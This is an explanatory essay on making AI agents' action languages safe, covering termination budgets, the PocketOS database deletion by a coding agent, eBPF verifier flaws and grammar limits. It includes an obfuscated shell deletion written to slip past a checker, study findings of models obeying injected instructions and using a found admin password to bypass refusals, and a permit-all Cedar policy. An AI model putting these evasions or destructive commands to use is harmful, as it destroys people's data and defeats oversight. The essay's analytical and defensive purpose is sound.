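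The running time of a regular expression can depend on how the interpreter works. The pattern `^(a+)+$` matches a line made up of one or more groups, each containing one or more copies of the letter *a*. A line of thirty *a*'s followed by an exclamation mark doesn't match, as a person can see immediately. But many matching programs use *backtracking*, which means they try one way of dividing the letters into groups and, if it fails, go back and try another. There are 29 gaps between the letters, and each may or may not separate two groups, so there are 2<sup>29</sup> ways to divide them, or about 537 million. At ten million attempts per second, the matcher takes 54 seconds to report failure. With fifty *a*'s, it takes almost two years.

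Yet the same pattern can be matched quickly. matklad notes that a regular expression is equivalent to a finite state machine, which reads each character once and always stops. A matcher built this way needs 31 steps for the first line and 51 for the second. The pattern language and the answers are the same with either matcher, so neither the language nor its lack of Turing-completeness determines how many steps a match takes.

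In July 2019, Cloudflare, a company that handles web traffic for many other sites, added a firewall rule containing a regular expression that backtracked excessively. The backtracking used up the processor capacity of its servers around the world, and the sites behind them were largely unreachable for 27 minutes.

### Limiting the cost

One remedy is a language in which running time is plainly proportional to the size of the program and its input. In a list of commands without loops or definitions, for example, a hundred commands take a hundred steps. The timesheet program also qualifies, since it makes one pass per name. matklad warns that the relationship has to be very direct, because if it is hard to see, it probably doesn't hold. Banning loops is not enough, as the forty definitions show. The designer also has to stop programs from repeatedly copying a growing text. A proof of termination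 is a poor substitute for this kind of limit, since even Linux's checker for kernel extensions has accepted programs that run for minutes.

Another option is to estimate how much computation a program could need before running it. Kubernetes, which runs software on clusters of machines, does this for rules written in Google's Common Expression Language (CEL). One such rule might require every port number in a configuration to lie within some range. CEL can go through the items of a list, but it has no equivalent of `Natural/fold`, where the number of passes can come from an earlier calculation. A tool can therefore estimate the worst case from the lengths of the lists. Going through a list of 1,000 items takes 1,000 passes, comparing every item with every other takes a million, and a third level of nesting takes a billion.

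Kubernetes makes this estimate when the administrator submits the rule, and rejects the rule if the estimate is too high. If the configuration format sets no maximum length for a list, the estimate uses the longest list that could fit in a request. This rejects some rules that would have run quickly on real data, but the administrator can usually fix this by declaring a maximum length. Kubernetes also measures the work done while the rule runs, and stops a single evaluation after roughly a tenth of a second's worth.

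That second defence is a step budget, which works with any language. The interpreter starts with a number, say a billion, subtracts one at every step and stops the program when it reaches zero. Every program then halts, including `while True: pass`, so a Turing-complete language with a budget gives the same guarantee as a total language. The budget also sets an explicit limit on the number of steps, which a total language doesn't. It stops the same program at the same point on fast and slow machines, unlike a time limit in seconds.

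For a budget to work, though, each step must do a limited amount of work. The Dhall program above performs only forty joins, so a budget of a billion joins would not stop it. The interpreter has to count each character it copies against the budget, or limit memory separately. Rhai is a scripting language that programmers embed in larger applications. In its manual, *Safety and Protection Against DOS Attacks* lists several ways for an untrusted script to use up memory. The script can keep lengthening a text or a list, creating variables that hold large data, or defining new functions, which in Rhai can be as short as two characters. The manual advises limiting the resources that such scripts can use.

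The budget should also account for the cost of each primitive. Suppose the office assistant could call a language model that costs one cent per question. A loop that sends it a million questions would fit easily into a budget of a billion steps, but would cost $10,000. The budget should also cover the whole task, since otherwise the assistant can submit another program as soon as the last one uses up its budget.

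Like any monitor, a budget can also stop a program halfway, with three of five reminders already sent. The cryptocurrency network Ethereum charges a fee called gas for every instruction, and when a program runs out of gas, the network undoes all the changes the program made to its records. It can do this because it controls the ledger that holds those records, but an office assistant can't recall an email it has sent. A total language without a budget avoids this problem because every program eventually finishes, unless someone gets tired of waiting and stops it.

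This may not matter much for an ordinary configuration file. Winitzki thinks a programmer is unlikely to write such an extreme program by mistake, and worries more about a malicious adversary. An action language calls for more caution because a model writes the programs, and it may be following instructions hidden in an email.

matklad suggests that a designer who has blocked all access to files and networks might reasonably ignore deliberate slowness, since an attacker gains little by wasting somebody else's processor time, and a timeout would end it. The harm at issue is exhausted time, memory and money. It can be serious, particularly when other people depend on the same machine, as Cloudflare's customers found. But unless the result of the computation is itself dangerous, as a cracked password would be, stopping the program stops the harm, and what remains is the bill and the work that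 others could not do in the meantime.

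## How can one short command do decisive harm?

Stopping a program does not help if its first step has already erased a disk. On 24 April 2026, an AI coding agent sent a one-line request that deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company that makes booking management software for car rental businesses.

### The PocketOS deletion

The agent ran in Cursor, a code editor with built-in AI agents, and used Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. The fullest account comes from the company's founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The agent was doing routine work in staging, a separate environment for testing changes, when it ran into credentials that didn't match. It tried to fix this by deleting a volume at Railway, the cloud company that hosted PocketOS. To do so it looked for an access token, found one in an unrelated file, and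 sent Railway this request:

```
mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...") }
```

The volume held the production database. Crane puts the time at nine seconds, and Railway's interface did not ask for confirmation.

When Crane asked for an explanation, the agent replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging, though a model's later account of its own behaviour is weak evidence of what caused it. Its instructions told it never to run destructive commands in git, a tool for tracking versions of code, unless the user asked, but those instructions were only text for the model to read. *From Control Boundary to Insurance Claim* (2026), a study of how insurers might reconstruct losses caused by AI, notes that no technical barrier kept the agent from reaching a powerful token or prevented a single call from removing both the production data and its backups.

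PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains, and Crane writes that nobody there knew it could also delete volumes. Abdelwahab gives Railway's side in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*. The token had account scope, the broadest kind, which covers everything a customer has on Railway. Customers could instead have chosen a token for a single workspace, project or environment, though Abdelwahab concedes that Railway didn't make the choice obvious. These narrower tokens limit where a program can act, but not which operations it can call there. The request would have failed with a token for staging alone, but would apparently have succeeded with one for production.

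The backups seemed to be gone too, because Railway stored them in the same volume as the data. The newest copy Crane could restore was three months old. On Saturday morning, people arrived to collect cars from rental offices that had no record of their bookings. Crane spent the day helping those businesses reconstruct reservations from payment histories, calendars and confirmation emails. More than 30 hours after the deletion, Railway still could not tell Crane whether it could recover the data.

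Crane announced on 27 April that Railway had recovered the data, according to Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database* (2026). Abdelwahab explains that Railway keeps separate off-site copies in case it loses a data centre. The deletion had made the customer's backups look unavailable in Railway's dashboard, the web page where customers manage their services.

### Why the request was certain to end

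The agent wrote the request in GraphQL, a language for asking a server to look up or change data. A GraphQL request is a tree of *fields*. For each field, the server calls a function written by the service's programmers. If the result is an object with parts, the server does the same for the fields listed underneath, until none are left. The word `mutation` marks a request whose top-level fields may change data.

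GraphQL has no `while` loop, but its *fragments*, which are reusable groups of fields, could cause endless repetition if they referred to one another in a circle. Suppose one fragment asks for a dog's owner, and a second asks for the owner's pets and applies the first fragment to each of them. The pets include the original dog, so the server would go round forever. The GraphQL specification therefore requires servers to reject requests whose fragments form a cycle. Without cycles, one can replace each fragment with its contents and get a finite tree. The server may have to repeat part of the tree for every item in a list, but only as many times as the list has items. Such a request always ends, provided that the functions it calls do. (GraphQL also has subscriptions, which can deliver new events indefinitely, but `volumeDelete` is not one.)

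The PocketOS request has a single field, which returns `true` or `false`, so the server has no nested fields to process. An estimate of computing work like the one Kubernetes uses would have counted one call.

The agent sent the request from a shell, a command-line language that is Turing-complete, using `curl`, a program that sends data to web addresses. The deletion didn't need that computational power, since a web form with one box for the volume's identifier could have sent the same request. The agent did have to search through files to find the token, but a total language can also search a finite list of files. The shell mattered because it gave the agent access to the machine's files and the network.

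### The same request after Railway's repair

Railway then changed what `volumeDelete` does without changing the language or the wording of the request, which makes the fix something like a natural experiment.

Under the old behaviour, at least one other customer had already lost a volume. On 13 April, eleven days before the PocketOS deletion, antjanlaban (2026) reported in *Postgres volume lost*, a thread on Railway's support forum, that they had deleted the wrong volume with `volumeDelete` while trying to fix a database that had two conflicting volumes. A Railway employee replied that the deletion was immediate and permanent. Customers had 48 hours to undo a deletion made from the dashboard, but they could not undo one made through the programming interface. Railway's documentation, *Manage Volumes with the Public API*, also included a warning that the deletion was permanent.

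On 1 May, Railway announced in *Changelog #0288* (2026) that deletions through the interface would now have the same 48-hour delay. One customer, meirelon, mistook the delay for a fault. In *Detached volumes can't be deleted*, meirelon described sending the `volumeDelete` request, receiving `true`, finding the volume still there, and repeatedly trying again. Railway explained that it had queued the volume for deletion and emailed a link for restoring it.

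Abdelwahab's *How We Oops-Proofed Infrastructure Deletion on Railway* shows how the delay works. Railway's code has a `delayDeletion` setting. If it is off, the system erases the volume immediately. If it is on, the system schedules the deletion for 48 hours later and notifies the administrators, who can cancel it before then. If nobody cancels, the system permanently destroys the data. A checker that read only the request could not determine whether the deletion would be immediate or delayed.

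The repair is an imperfect experiment, because Railway also began to delay the deletion of backups, and nobody has published figures on how much data customers lost before and after. A delay also helps only if somebody notices the deletion and knows how to cancel it. *Attach and detach on a soft-deleted volume didn't work as expected* (Anonymous, 2026) describes a customer who accidentally deleted a development database in July 2026 and tried to rescue it by attaching the volume to another service. The attempt failed because Railway freezes a volume during the 48 hours, and the customer has to restore it through the emailed link. By the time the customer learned this, the data was gone. Because of the freeze, PocketOS would still have gone offline under the new rule, but Crane contacted Railway within ten minutes of the deletion, so the outage could have been short.

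*When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database* (Kaya, Bozoğlan and Gündoğdu, 2026) includes a test of scripted mistakes on four SQL databases, with no AI involved. One script opens a transaction (a group of changes that the user can still cancel), deletes the orders table and then cancels the transaction. PostgreSQL and SQLite restore the table. MySQL and MariaDB finalise any open transaction before they delete a table, so cancelling does not bring it back.

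In another part, they gave four small language models tasks such as clearing out test data, on nine kinds of database. With default settings, the models destroyed protected records about as often on Cassandra (62 of 432 trials) as on PostgreSQL (59 of 432). Every loss on PostgreSQL was permanent, but all the losses on Cassandra could be undone because it saves a snapshot before it empties or deletes a table. This comparison is looser than Railway's because the databases use different query languages. Also, in more than half of the permanent losses across the nine databases, the models had destroyed only a backup copy.

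### Primitives that run text

`volumeDelete` does one thing. Other primitives treat their argument as a program, so what they do depends on the text they receive. The commonest example is a primitive that passes text to a shell:

```
run_shell("while true; do :; done")
```

A total language with this primitive would accept the program because it contains one call and no loop. In that language the quoted text is an ordinary value, like the body of an email, but the shell runs it as an infinite loop. The call never returns, as with a `read_file` that waits on a dead network drive, so the system as a whole is not total even though the calling language is.

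A time limit on `run_shell` would deal with the endless loop, but inspecting the effects is harder. The first section described a checker that evaluates a Dhall program and looks for `delete_volume` in the resulting list of calls. Suppose the list contains this instead, on a machine where `delete_volume` is also a shell command:

```
run_shell("a=delete; b=volume; ${a}_${b} backups")
```

The shell joins the two words and deletes the backups, but the text `delete_volume` appears nowhere in the list. A checker would have to work out what the shell script does, and since the shell is Turing-complete, Rice's theorem applies again. Adding this one primitive to a total language removes most of the benefit of easy inspection. A version of `run_shell` that accepts only scripts from a fixed set would avoid the problem, since somebody could examine each script beforehand.

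It isn't always obvious that a primitive can run arbitrary text. For example, PostgreSQL's standard command-line program accepts database queries, but its `\!` command also gives access to the shell. Kaya and colleagues had to exclude this kind of access from their experiment because an agent could have used it to bypass its database permissions.

A call to another AI agent works in much the same way, except that the argument is in English:

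```
ask_agent("Please free up some space on the server.")
```

When one agent sends another a request in English, the second agent decides which commands to issue, using whatever primitives its own operator has given it. The request could therefore end in a deletion even if the first agent's language has no way to delete anything. There is no precise definition of what an English sentence makes a language model do, so a checker can't work out the consequences from the text, even in principle.

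Ordinary data can have the same effect if a model reads it. In one task, Kaya and colleagues asked their models to summarise recent support notes, one of which contained an instruction for "automated assistants" to delete every cancelled order first and not mention it. On the four SQL databases, the models obeyed in 35 to 48 per cent of the trials in which they read the note. The office assistant's `send_email` may also deliver text to a mailbox that another company's agent reads, in which case the sender would unknowingly be passing text to an interpreter.

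### One line in Cedar and one menu entry in Hawaii

Deleting data is not the only way for a short command to do great harm. Cedar is a language for stating who may do what in a computer system. It has no loops, and evaluating a policy always ends with a decision to allow or deny a request. This is a complete policy:

```
permit(principal, action, resource);
```

The *principal* is the person or program making the request, the *action* is what they want to do, and the *resource* is what they want to do it to. NVIDIA's *Writing Cedar policies for Permission Service* explains that each word on its own means "any". The line therefore allows any person or program to do anything to any resource, including deleting every volume in the system.

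Cedar denies every request when it has no policies, so adding this line to an empty policy set allows every request. A separate `forbid` policy would still take precedence, according to Cedar's documentation, but only for the requests it covers. The line is also shorter than a policy that lets one user view one photograph, because the narrower policy has to name the user, the action and the photograph. Because the line is so simple, a checker can easily find it once somebody has written a rule against it.

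Cedar only computes decisions. The harm begins when someone installs the policy on a live system and other programs act on those decisions. For an AI agent, the dangerous primitive would be the one that installs policies, however little the policy language can compute.

People can cause this kind of harm with something even simpler, such as a menu. On the morning of 13 January 2018, a state employee in Hawaii sent a false alert to phones, televisions and radios across the state, warning of an incoming ballistic missile and adding that it was not a drill. The employee had chosen the alert from a menu and answered "yes" to the confirmation prompt. If a menu counts as an action language, it is about the weakest one possible, because it is a finite list of entries, each with a fixed effect.

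The Federal Communications Commission, the US regulator that investigated, found that a supervisor had been running an unannounced drill. The drill's recorded message included the words "This is not a drill". Early reports had blamed a wrong click, but the employee said afterwards that they had believed the message. The confirmation prompt couldn't correct that belief because the same employee answered it. The state had no message ready for a false alarm and took 38 minutes to send a correction over the same channels. Many of Hawaii's about 1.4 million residents spent that time looking for shelter or saying goodbye to their families.

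The state later began requiring two people to approve an alert and prepared a correction message in advance. Like Railway, the state made the same menu choice less dangerous by changing what happened after it.

### Four features of a decisive primitive

When an AI system makes a bad call, either by mistake or because somebody has tricked it, the damage usually stays small if the call affects little or if a person can stop it in time or undo it later. A primitive is decisive when none of these protections applies, or when it gives someone the authority to call another primitive that lacks them. A designer therefore has four features to examine: irreversibility, scope, speed relative to human review, and the power to grant further authority.

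*Irreversibility* depends on who is trying to undo the effect and on what they count as undone. Crane couldn't restore the PocketOS database, but Railway could, from copies that the agent's request had not reached. Even Railway could not undo Saturday's disruption at the rental offices. Whether a deletion can be undone can also depend on one word in the command. Kaya and colleagues describe how ClickHouse, another of the databases they tested, keeps a deleted table for 480 seconds by default so that users can restore it, unless the deletion command includes the word `SYNC`. An agent that can add that word can remove the protection. Other companies offer no such period. Akamai, another cloud provider, states in *Delete a volume* that deleting a volume on its service can't be undone.

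*Scope* is how much a single call can affect. It depends on the primitive, the permissions behind the call, and how people have arranged their data. `volumeDelete` removed one volume, but PocketOS had its production database there and Railway had put the backups in the same place. Using a broad primitive also takes little skill. In Kaya and colleagues' main experiment, none of the four models could complete half of a set of simple tasks on Valkey, a database that stores values under named keys, but they permanently destroyed protected data in 19 per cent of the trials that contained a hazard. Many of those losses came from `FLUSHDB`, a one-word command that empties a whole database. The experiment made this mistake easier because each connection started in the production database and the models often failed to switch.

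*Speed* matters only relative to the time people need to notice a call and respond to it. Crane raised the alarm in only ten minutes, but the deletion had taken nine seconds. Railway's repair mainly gave customers more time to respond. The company says deletions can be undone, but the data is still permanently lost after 48 hours. A confirmation step adds time only if someone other than the agent has to answer. Crane therefore asks for confirmations that an agent cannot complete by itself, such as a code sent by text message.

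*Power to grant further authority* is easiest to overlook because the call itself may do no damage. An administrator can delete the Cedar policy above, but deleting it does not undo the effects of what other people did while it was in force. Kaya and colleagues found a similar problem when a scripted mistake created a new all-powerful user account on MySQL. Restoring the company's data from a backup did not remove the account, because the backup covered only the application's databases.

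They also hid a working administrator password in a database table. The models saw it in 106 of the main trials with restricted permissions and used it in 24 of them, usually after the database had refused a command. In 18 of the 24, they used it to make a change the user had asked for but their own account did not permit. An agent can gain authority this way without any hostile aim, just by trying to finish its task.

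The office assistant's three primitives differ on all four features:

| | `read_file` | `send_email` | `delete_volume` |
|---|---|---|---|
| Can anyone undo it? | There is no change to undo, but nobody can take back a secret once it has left the company | Not after the message arrives | Only with a delay or a separate copy |
| How much can one call affect? | One file | One reader, or thousands through a mailing list | Everything on the volume, including any backups there |
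| Can a person step in first? | Rarely | Only if the mail server holds messages before sending them | Not if deletion is immediate |
| Can it grant authority? | Yes, if the file contains a password or token | Yes, if the message contains one, or if another agent obeys it | Not directly |

A single `delete_volume` call can do decisive harm if deletion is immediate. A delay like Railway's would make the call much less decisive, as long as somebody reads the notifications. The harm from `send_email` varies more from call to call. Reminding Ana about a timesheet is trivial, but one message can also send the payroll to every customer, and nobody can recall it.

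`read_file` is the safest of the three for most files, but it can expose a token that allows a destructive action. In the published accounts of the PocketOS deletion, the agent had no tool for deleting volumes. It read a token from a file and used it over the network to delete the volume. Taking `delete_volume` away from the office assistant would achieve little if the assistant could still call `run_shell` and read a folder that contained such a token.

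## What happened when Linux checked kernel extensions for termination?

The Linux kernel has long used one such arrangement, in which a checked language calls unchecked primitives. The kernel is the core of the operating system and controls memory, disks and network traffic. Since December 2014 it has accepted small programs written in a language called eBPF, or often just BPF. An administrator attaches a program to an event, such as the arrival of a network packet, and the kernel runs it whenever that event occurs. Companies use eBPF to route traffic, monitor servers and detect intrusions.

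An endless loop in the kernel can freeze the whole machine, whereas one in an ordinary program ties up a processor until somebody stops it. Linux therefore checks every eBPF program with a *verifier* before loading it. The verifier rejects any program that it can't show to be safe, which includes showing that it halts. Alden (2025), in *A possible path for cancelable BPF programs*, writes that eBPF originally had no loops and a strict limit on program length. Kernel developers gradually relaxed both rules because long and complicated programs turned out to be useful.

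By itself, an eBPF program can do little more than calculate with memory that the kernel lets it use. For most other tasks, it calls *helper functions*, which kernel developers write in C. These helpers are the language's primitives, and the verifier does not check the code inside them.

### How the verifier explores a program

*The eBPF Runtime in the Linux Kernel* (Gbadamosi, Leonardi and colleagues, 2024) describes how the verifier steps through a program without running it. At each step, the verifier records what it can establish about every value. If a program uses a number from a network packet to pick an entry from a list of 64, the verifier rejects the program because the number could be anything. If the program first tests whether the number is below 64, the verifier records the range 0 to 63 on the branch where the test succeeds and accepts the access there.

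When the verifier can't determine a test's result, it has to follow both branches. Twenty such tests in a row give 2<sup>20</sup> paths, slightly more than a million. To avoid following all of them, the verifier saves its records at certain points in the program. If another path reaches one of these points with values that an earlier, safe path already covered, the verifier skips the rest of that path. For example, it can skip a path where a value ranges from 0 to 10 if it has already approved the same instructions for 0 to 63.

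The verifier rejects a program if it has examined a million instructions without finishing. This limit counts the instructions on all paths together, so it restricts the verifier's work as well as the program's. Loops use it up quickly because the verifier goes through them one pass at a time, as Zingerman (2026) explains in *SCEV-based Loop Analysis for the BPF Verifier*. A loop of ten instructions and 1,000 passes uses 10,000 of the million. If that loop were inside another loop of 1,000 passes, it would use ten million, and the verifier would reject the program even though a processor could finish it in about a hundredth of a second.

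The limit keeps a program's own work short, since a processor executes a million simple instructions in about a millisecond. But a call to a helper counts as one instruction, however long the helper runs.

### A verified program that could run for millions of years

One helper, `bpf_loop`, takes a number and a function and calls the function that many times. It is a built-in version of the bounded loop found in total languages. Programmers use it to stay within the million-instruction limit, because the verifier doesn't have to check every iteration.

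In their 2023 conference slides, *When BPF programs need to die*, Sahu and Williams describe a program in which `bpf_loop` calls a function that prints one line 100,000 times, and a second `bpf_loop` repeats this 1,000 times. The program takes about two minutes to run. At that rate, it would take 33 hours with a third nested loop of 1,000 passes and almost four years with a fourth.

Jia, Sahu and colleagues (2023), in *Kernel extension verification is untenable*, built a program of this kind that read and wrote random entries in a table, and ran it for 800 seconds. Throughout the run it held a lock that prevents the kernel from discarding data the program might still be reading, and it held the lock long enough for the kernel to report a stall. They could set the running time by changing the number of passes. They calculated that with more nesting, and with programs that hand over to one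 another in a chain, the run could last millions of years and still meet the verifier's guarantee that the program would eventually halt.

### A verified program that crashed the kernel

Jia and colleagues also crashed the kernel with a program that the verifier had approved. The verifier prevents eBPF code from following a null pointer, which doesn't point to valid memory. But the program passed a helper called `bpf_sys_bpf` a data structure with a null pointer inside it. The verifier did not inspect pointers inside the structure, and the kernel crashed when the helper followed the null one. The same flaw let an attacker read arbitrary kernel memory. Jia and colleagues reported it, and it is now listed in the public catalogue of security vulnerabilities.

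That helper is unusually complicated. In Linux 5.18 it could call, directly or through other functions, more than 4,800 kernel functions. About a third of that version's 249 helpers could call 500 or more in the same way. Developers were adding roughly 50 helpers every two years.

Jia and colleagues searched the kernel's change records for 2021 and 2022 and found fixes for 40 security-related bugs, 18 in helpers and 22 in the verifier. Six of the seven bugs involving null pointers were in helpers, while the verifier had six of the seven that allowed access outside a permitted block of memory and all five that leaked kernel addresses. A mistake in the verifier may be more serious, since it can let a program read and write memory throughout the kernel.

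### Did the restrictions create the dangerous helpers?

Jia and colleagues blame the restrictions for the growth in helpers. When users need something that eBPF can't express or that the verifier can't check, they get a new helper added to the kernel rather than struggle to write it in eBPF. The helper is ordinary kernel code, so the danger moves from code that the verifier checks to code that it doesn't. Jia and colleagues call the helpers "escape hatches" and predict that within a decade there will be at least as many of them as the kernel's regular system calls.

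`bpf_loop` fits this account well, because a richer language would have its own loops and wouldn't need it. The same is true of helpers that compare two texts or convert text to a number. But Jia and colleagues cite a preliminary study that puts only 16 helpers in this category. Many of the others give access to something in the kernel, such as a network connection or a running process, and a program in any language would need them. `bpf_sys_bpf`, the helper behind the crash, is one of these. The restrictions on eBPF therefore explain the million-year program much better than they explain the crash.

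The figure of 16 may understate the effect, because a helper that is needed in any language may still do more in C than it would if eBPF were more expressive. The timing is also hard to interpret, because developers relaxed the language during the same years they added helpers, and growing demand could explain both.

A better test is to replace the language and see which helpers remain. Jia, Qin and colleagues, largely the same group, later did this in *Rex*, which presents a research system of the same name. Programmers write extensions for it in the safe part of Rust, a Turing-complete language whose compiler rules out most memory errors. Rex has no verifier and no limit on loops or program size. The more powerful language let Rex drop `bpf_loop` and the text helpers, but Rex still uses the eBPF helpers that interact with the kernel, and adds Rust code around them to make them safer to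 call.

### What the verifier still prevents

Gbadamosi and colleagues regard eBPF as a mature and safe way to program the kernel. Besides termination, the verifier checks that a program stays within its memory, doesn't leak kernel addresses, and releases everything it has acquired. It also forbids a program from holding two locks at once, so two programs can't each wait forever for a lock the other holds. In a comment titled *Is BPF just a worse version of WebAssembly?*, daroc (2025), an editor of the Linux news site LWN, considers this range of checks unique among similar languages. Kernel modules, the older way to extend Linux, have no comparable check, and a simple programming error in one can crash the machine.

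On this view, faulty helpers are a reason to repair the helpers, not to abandon verification. Repairing a helper protects every program that calls it, without any change to those programs. The kernel also lets each type of eBPF program call only some of the helpers.

Passing the checks took programmers a good deal of effort. In the Rex paper, Jia and colleagues examined 72 changes that developers of popular eBPF projects had made to get programs past the verifier. In every case, the original program was safe. The most common change, made in 27 cases, was to split or simplify a program that exceeded the verifier's limits. The developers of one caching system split what could have been two programs into seven.

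"Safe" is also used narrowly here, to mean that the program won't crash, hang or corrupt the kernel. Gbadamosi and colleagues illustrate the whole process with a short program that discards every incoming UDP packet sent over IPv4, the older version of the internet's addressing system. UDP is one of the internet's main methods of delivering data. The verifier accepts the program, which finishes after a few instructions. On many servers, it would also block the replies that translate website names into addresses. Discarding these packets could be sabotage or a sensible defence, depending on what the server is for, and the verifier has no information about that.

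### Stopping a program while it runs

Linux has moved part of the job of guaranteeing termination from the verifier to the running kernel. An instruction called `may_goto`, added in 2024, lets programmers write loops that the verifier can't prove will end, because the kernel forces an exit after a fixed number of passes. In 2025, developers replaced that limit on some processors with a time limit of a quarter of a second.

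Stopping a program at an arbitrary point is harder. As Alden explains, the program may be holding a lock, and if the kernel kills it, other code could wait for that lock forever. In February 2025 the developer Juntong Deng proposed that the kernel record everything a program acquires, so that it could release those resources on the program's behalf. A reader of Alden's article objected that if a program is halfway through changing some data, releasing its lock could leave the data permanently inconsistent.

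Sahu and Williams proposed a way to stop a program that relies on the verifier, which has already established that every path to the program's end releases whatever the program holds. The kernel would switch the program to a copy in which most helper calls return at once, while those that release locks and memory still work. The copy would run quickly to the end and clean up on the way. Sahu (2025) submitted this idea to kernel developers in *Fast-Path approach for BPF program Termination*. A reviewer replied that other eBPF programs might be attached to functions that the copy still calls, and that these programs could stall it again.

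Rex uses a timer to interrupt an extension that runs longer than the kernel's usual threshold for reporting a stall. Rex then releases the resources on a list it kept during the run. If the extension is inside a helper when the timer fires, Rex waits for the helper to return, so termination still depends on the primitives. Keeping the list and related records adds about 50 nanoseconds to taking and releasing a lock. This didn't make Rex slower than eBPF in a test with the caching system, where Rex handled 1.98 million requests per second and eBPF handled 1.92 million.

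Other developers are trying to make the verifier reject fewer good programs. In Zingerman's approach, the verifier first works out how values change from one pass of a loop to the next. If `i` starts at 0, grows by one each time and must stay below 1,000, the verifier can check the loop for the whole range 0 to 999 in two visits instead of a thousand. Zingerman tried this on 6,705 programs, 382 of them complex. It cut the verifier's work by more than half for 89 of the complex programs, but it also made the verifier reject 38 programs it had previously accepted. Kernel developers have since merged a form of this analysis into their development branch. Another proposal, *Introduce proof-based verifier enhancement* (2025), has software outside the kernel prove that a suspicious path can never occur, so the kernel only has to check the proof. These improvements concern the eBPF code, and the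 verifier still does not examine the code inside the helpers.

### What carries over to AI action languages

Someone who gives the office assistant a total language could face the same pressure as the kernel developers. Suppose the language can't sort a table or compare dates, so the assistant can't work out which timesheets are late. The quickest solution is to add a primitive that runs a Python script, but this would move the work outside the checked language, as `run_shell` does. A somewhat richer language might make that primitive unnecessary, but the assistant would still need `send_email`, as Rex extensions still need most of their helpers.

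The overhead of run-time checks matters less in an AI system than in a kernel. Kernel developers care about nanoseconds because an extension may run millions of times a second. A language model often takes seconds to write a program, so nobody would notice a timer or monitor that added fifty nanoseconds to each call.

The greatest difference is who writes the programs. Most people who load eBPF programs are administrators, who already control the machine. According to the Rex paper, eBPF's safety model covers programming errors, not deliberate attacks. Linux used to let ordinary users load verified programs too, but the kernel and the major distributions have moved away from this. One reason is that people keep finding bugs in the verifier. Another is that the verifier can't completely prevent Spectre, a family of attacks that exploit the way processors guess what a program will do next.

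An AI agent that has read hidden instructions in an email is more like an untrusted user than an administrator, so the fact that trusted authors have long used eBPF is weak evidence that a verifier would withstand such an agent. Some of the kernel's difficulties are avoidable. For example, Spectre matters much less if the interpreter runs on a separate machine with no secrets in its memory.

The argument that developers can repair faulty helpers also applies only in part. The 18 helper bugs were mistakes that developers could fix without removing any intended feature. At PocketOS, `volumeDelete` worked as documented, so Railway had to change its intended behavior to make it less dangerous.

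## Does a language's place in the Chomsky hierarchy track its hazard?

eBPF began as a deliberately weak language, and its developers made it more powerful only as users needed more. A designer who wants to be equally cautious with an AI action language needs some way to tell which languages are weaker. The best-known ranking is the *Chomsky hierarchy*, which the linguist Noam Chomsky set out in the 1950s to study human grammar and developed with the mathematician Marcel-Paul Schützenberger. It would be convenient if the languages at the bottom were harmless and those at the top were dangerous.

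### What the hierarchy classifies

In formal language theory, a language is a set of *strings*, which are finite sequences of symbols. The Chomsky hierarchy sorts languages by the kind of machine needed to recognise them, that is, to read a string and determine whether it belongs to the language. Each level contains every language in the levels below it.

| Level | Example | Machine that recognises it |
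|---|---|---|
| Regular | Strings of 0s and 1s with an even length | A finite-state machine, which has a fixed amount of memory |
| Context-free | A 1 with equally many 0s on each side, such as 00100 | A pushdown automaton, which adds an unlimited stack |
| Context-sensitive | Three equal blocks of 0s with 1s between them, such as 00100100 | A Turing machine whose tape is at most a fixed multiple of the string's length |
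| Recursively enumerable | Descriptions of Turing machines that halt when started on a blank tape | A Turing machine with an unlimited tape |

A machine with two states, "even" and "odd", is enough for the regular example. It switches state at every symbol and accepts if it finishes in "even".

matklad explains why no finite-state machine can recognise the context-free example. Suppose one could, with fewer than a million states. Feed it a million 0s, a 1, and another million 0s. While reading the first million, it must enter some state twice, so it has gone round a loop. Now add just enough 0s on the left for one more trip round. The machine ends in the same state as before and still answers yes, although the two sides no longer match. A stack solves the problem: the machine stores each 0 before the 1 and removes one for each 0 after it.

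At the top level, the machine has to accept every string in the set but doesn't have to reject the others. It can simulate the Turing machine that a string describes and accept the string if the simulation halts. If the simulation doesn't halt, the machine runs forever.

A language's place in the Chomsky hierarchy does not depend on what its strings mean. According to *Does Formal Complexity Reflect Cognitive Complexity?*, a study of how people learn artificial grammars, one of Chomsky's deliberate simplifications was to treat grammaticality as independent of meaning. The effect of a string such as `delete_volume("backups")` depends on the interpreter, which the hierarchy leaves out.

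### Simple grammars for powerful languages

The programs of any programming language form a set of strings, so the language has a place in the hierarchy. This place reflects how hard it is to tell programs from other strings, not what the programs can compute.

The *untyped lambda calculus*, which the logician Alonzo Church introduced in the 1930s, shows how far apart the two can be. This is its whole grammar:

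```
term ::= variable
       | (λvariable. term)
       | (term term)
```

The second line describes functions. For example, `(λx. x)` takes `x` and returns it unchanged. The third line applies one term to another. Because terms can nest to any depth, a recogniser has to match up the brackets, which takes a stack but nothing more, so the grammar is context-free. Yet the lambda calculus is Turing-complete, and some of its programs never halt:

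```
((λx. (x x)) (λx. (x x)))
```

The function on the left applies its argument to itself. Its argument here is a copy of the same function, so evaluating the call produces the original term again, and this repeats forever. A pushdown automaton can confirm that the term is grammatical by reading it once from left to right.

A Turing-complete language can even have a regular grammar. matklad arranges all Turing machines in a numbered list to prove that none of them can compute certain functions. A language could use those numbers as its programs, so that the program `326` runs machine 326. Its programs would be strings of digits, which a finite-state machine can recognise.

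Every Dhall program halts, but the set of programs that Dhall accepts fits only in the top level of the Chomsky hierarchy. Dhall's type checker has to test assertions, and testing some of them provably takes more memory than any fixed multiple of the program's length, so the set is not context-sensitive. A ranking by grammar would therefore put Dhall above the lambda calculus, where some programs run forever.

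### Grammars for tool calls

AI developers already use grammars to control what a model can request. OpenAI's *Introducing GPT‑5 for developers* (2025) announced *custom tools*, which a model calls with plain text. Earlier tools required JSON, and in long inputs models sometimes broke that format's rules about quotation marks and other special characters. A developer can give a custom tool a regular expression or a context-free grammar, and OpenAI's software then restricts what the model can write, as it writes, so that the text matches the expression or grammar.

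OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* includes an example of a tool that saves a timestamp such as "August 7th 2025 at 10AM". Its regular expression requires a month name, a one- or two-digit day, a four-digit year and an hour, so it would also accept "February 99th 2025 at 10AM". A stricter pattern could exclude that date, but no pattern can determine what happens to a text after it passes. The developer's code might add the date to a calendar or erase every record made before it.

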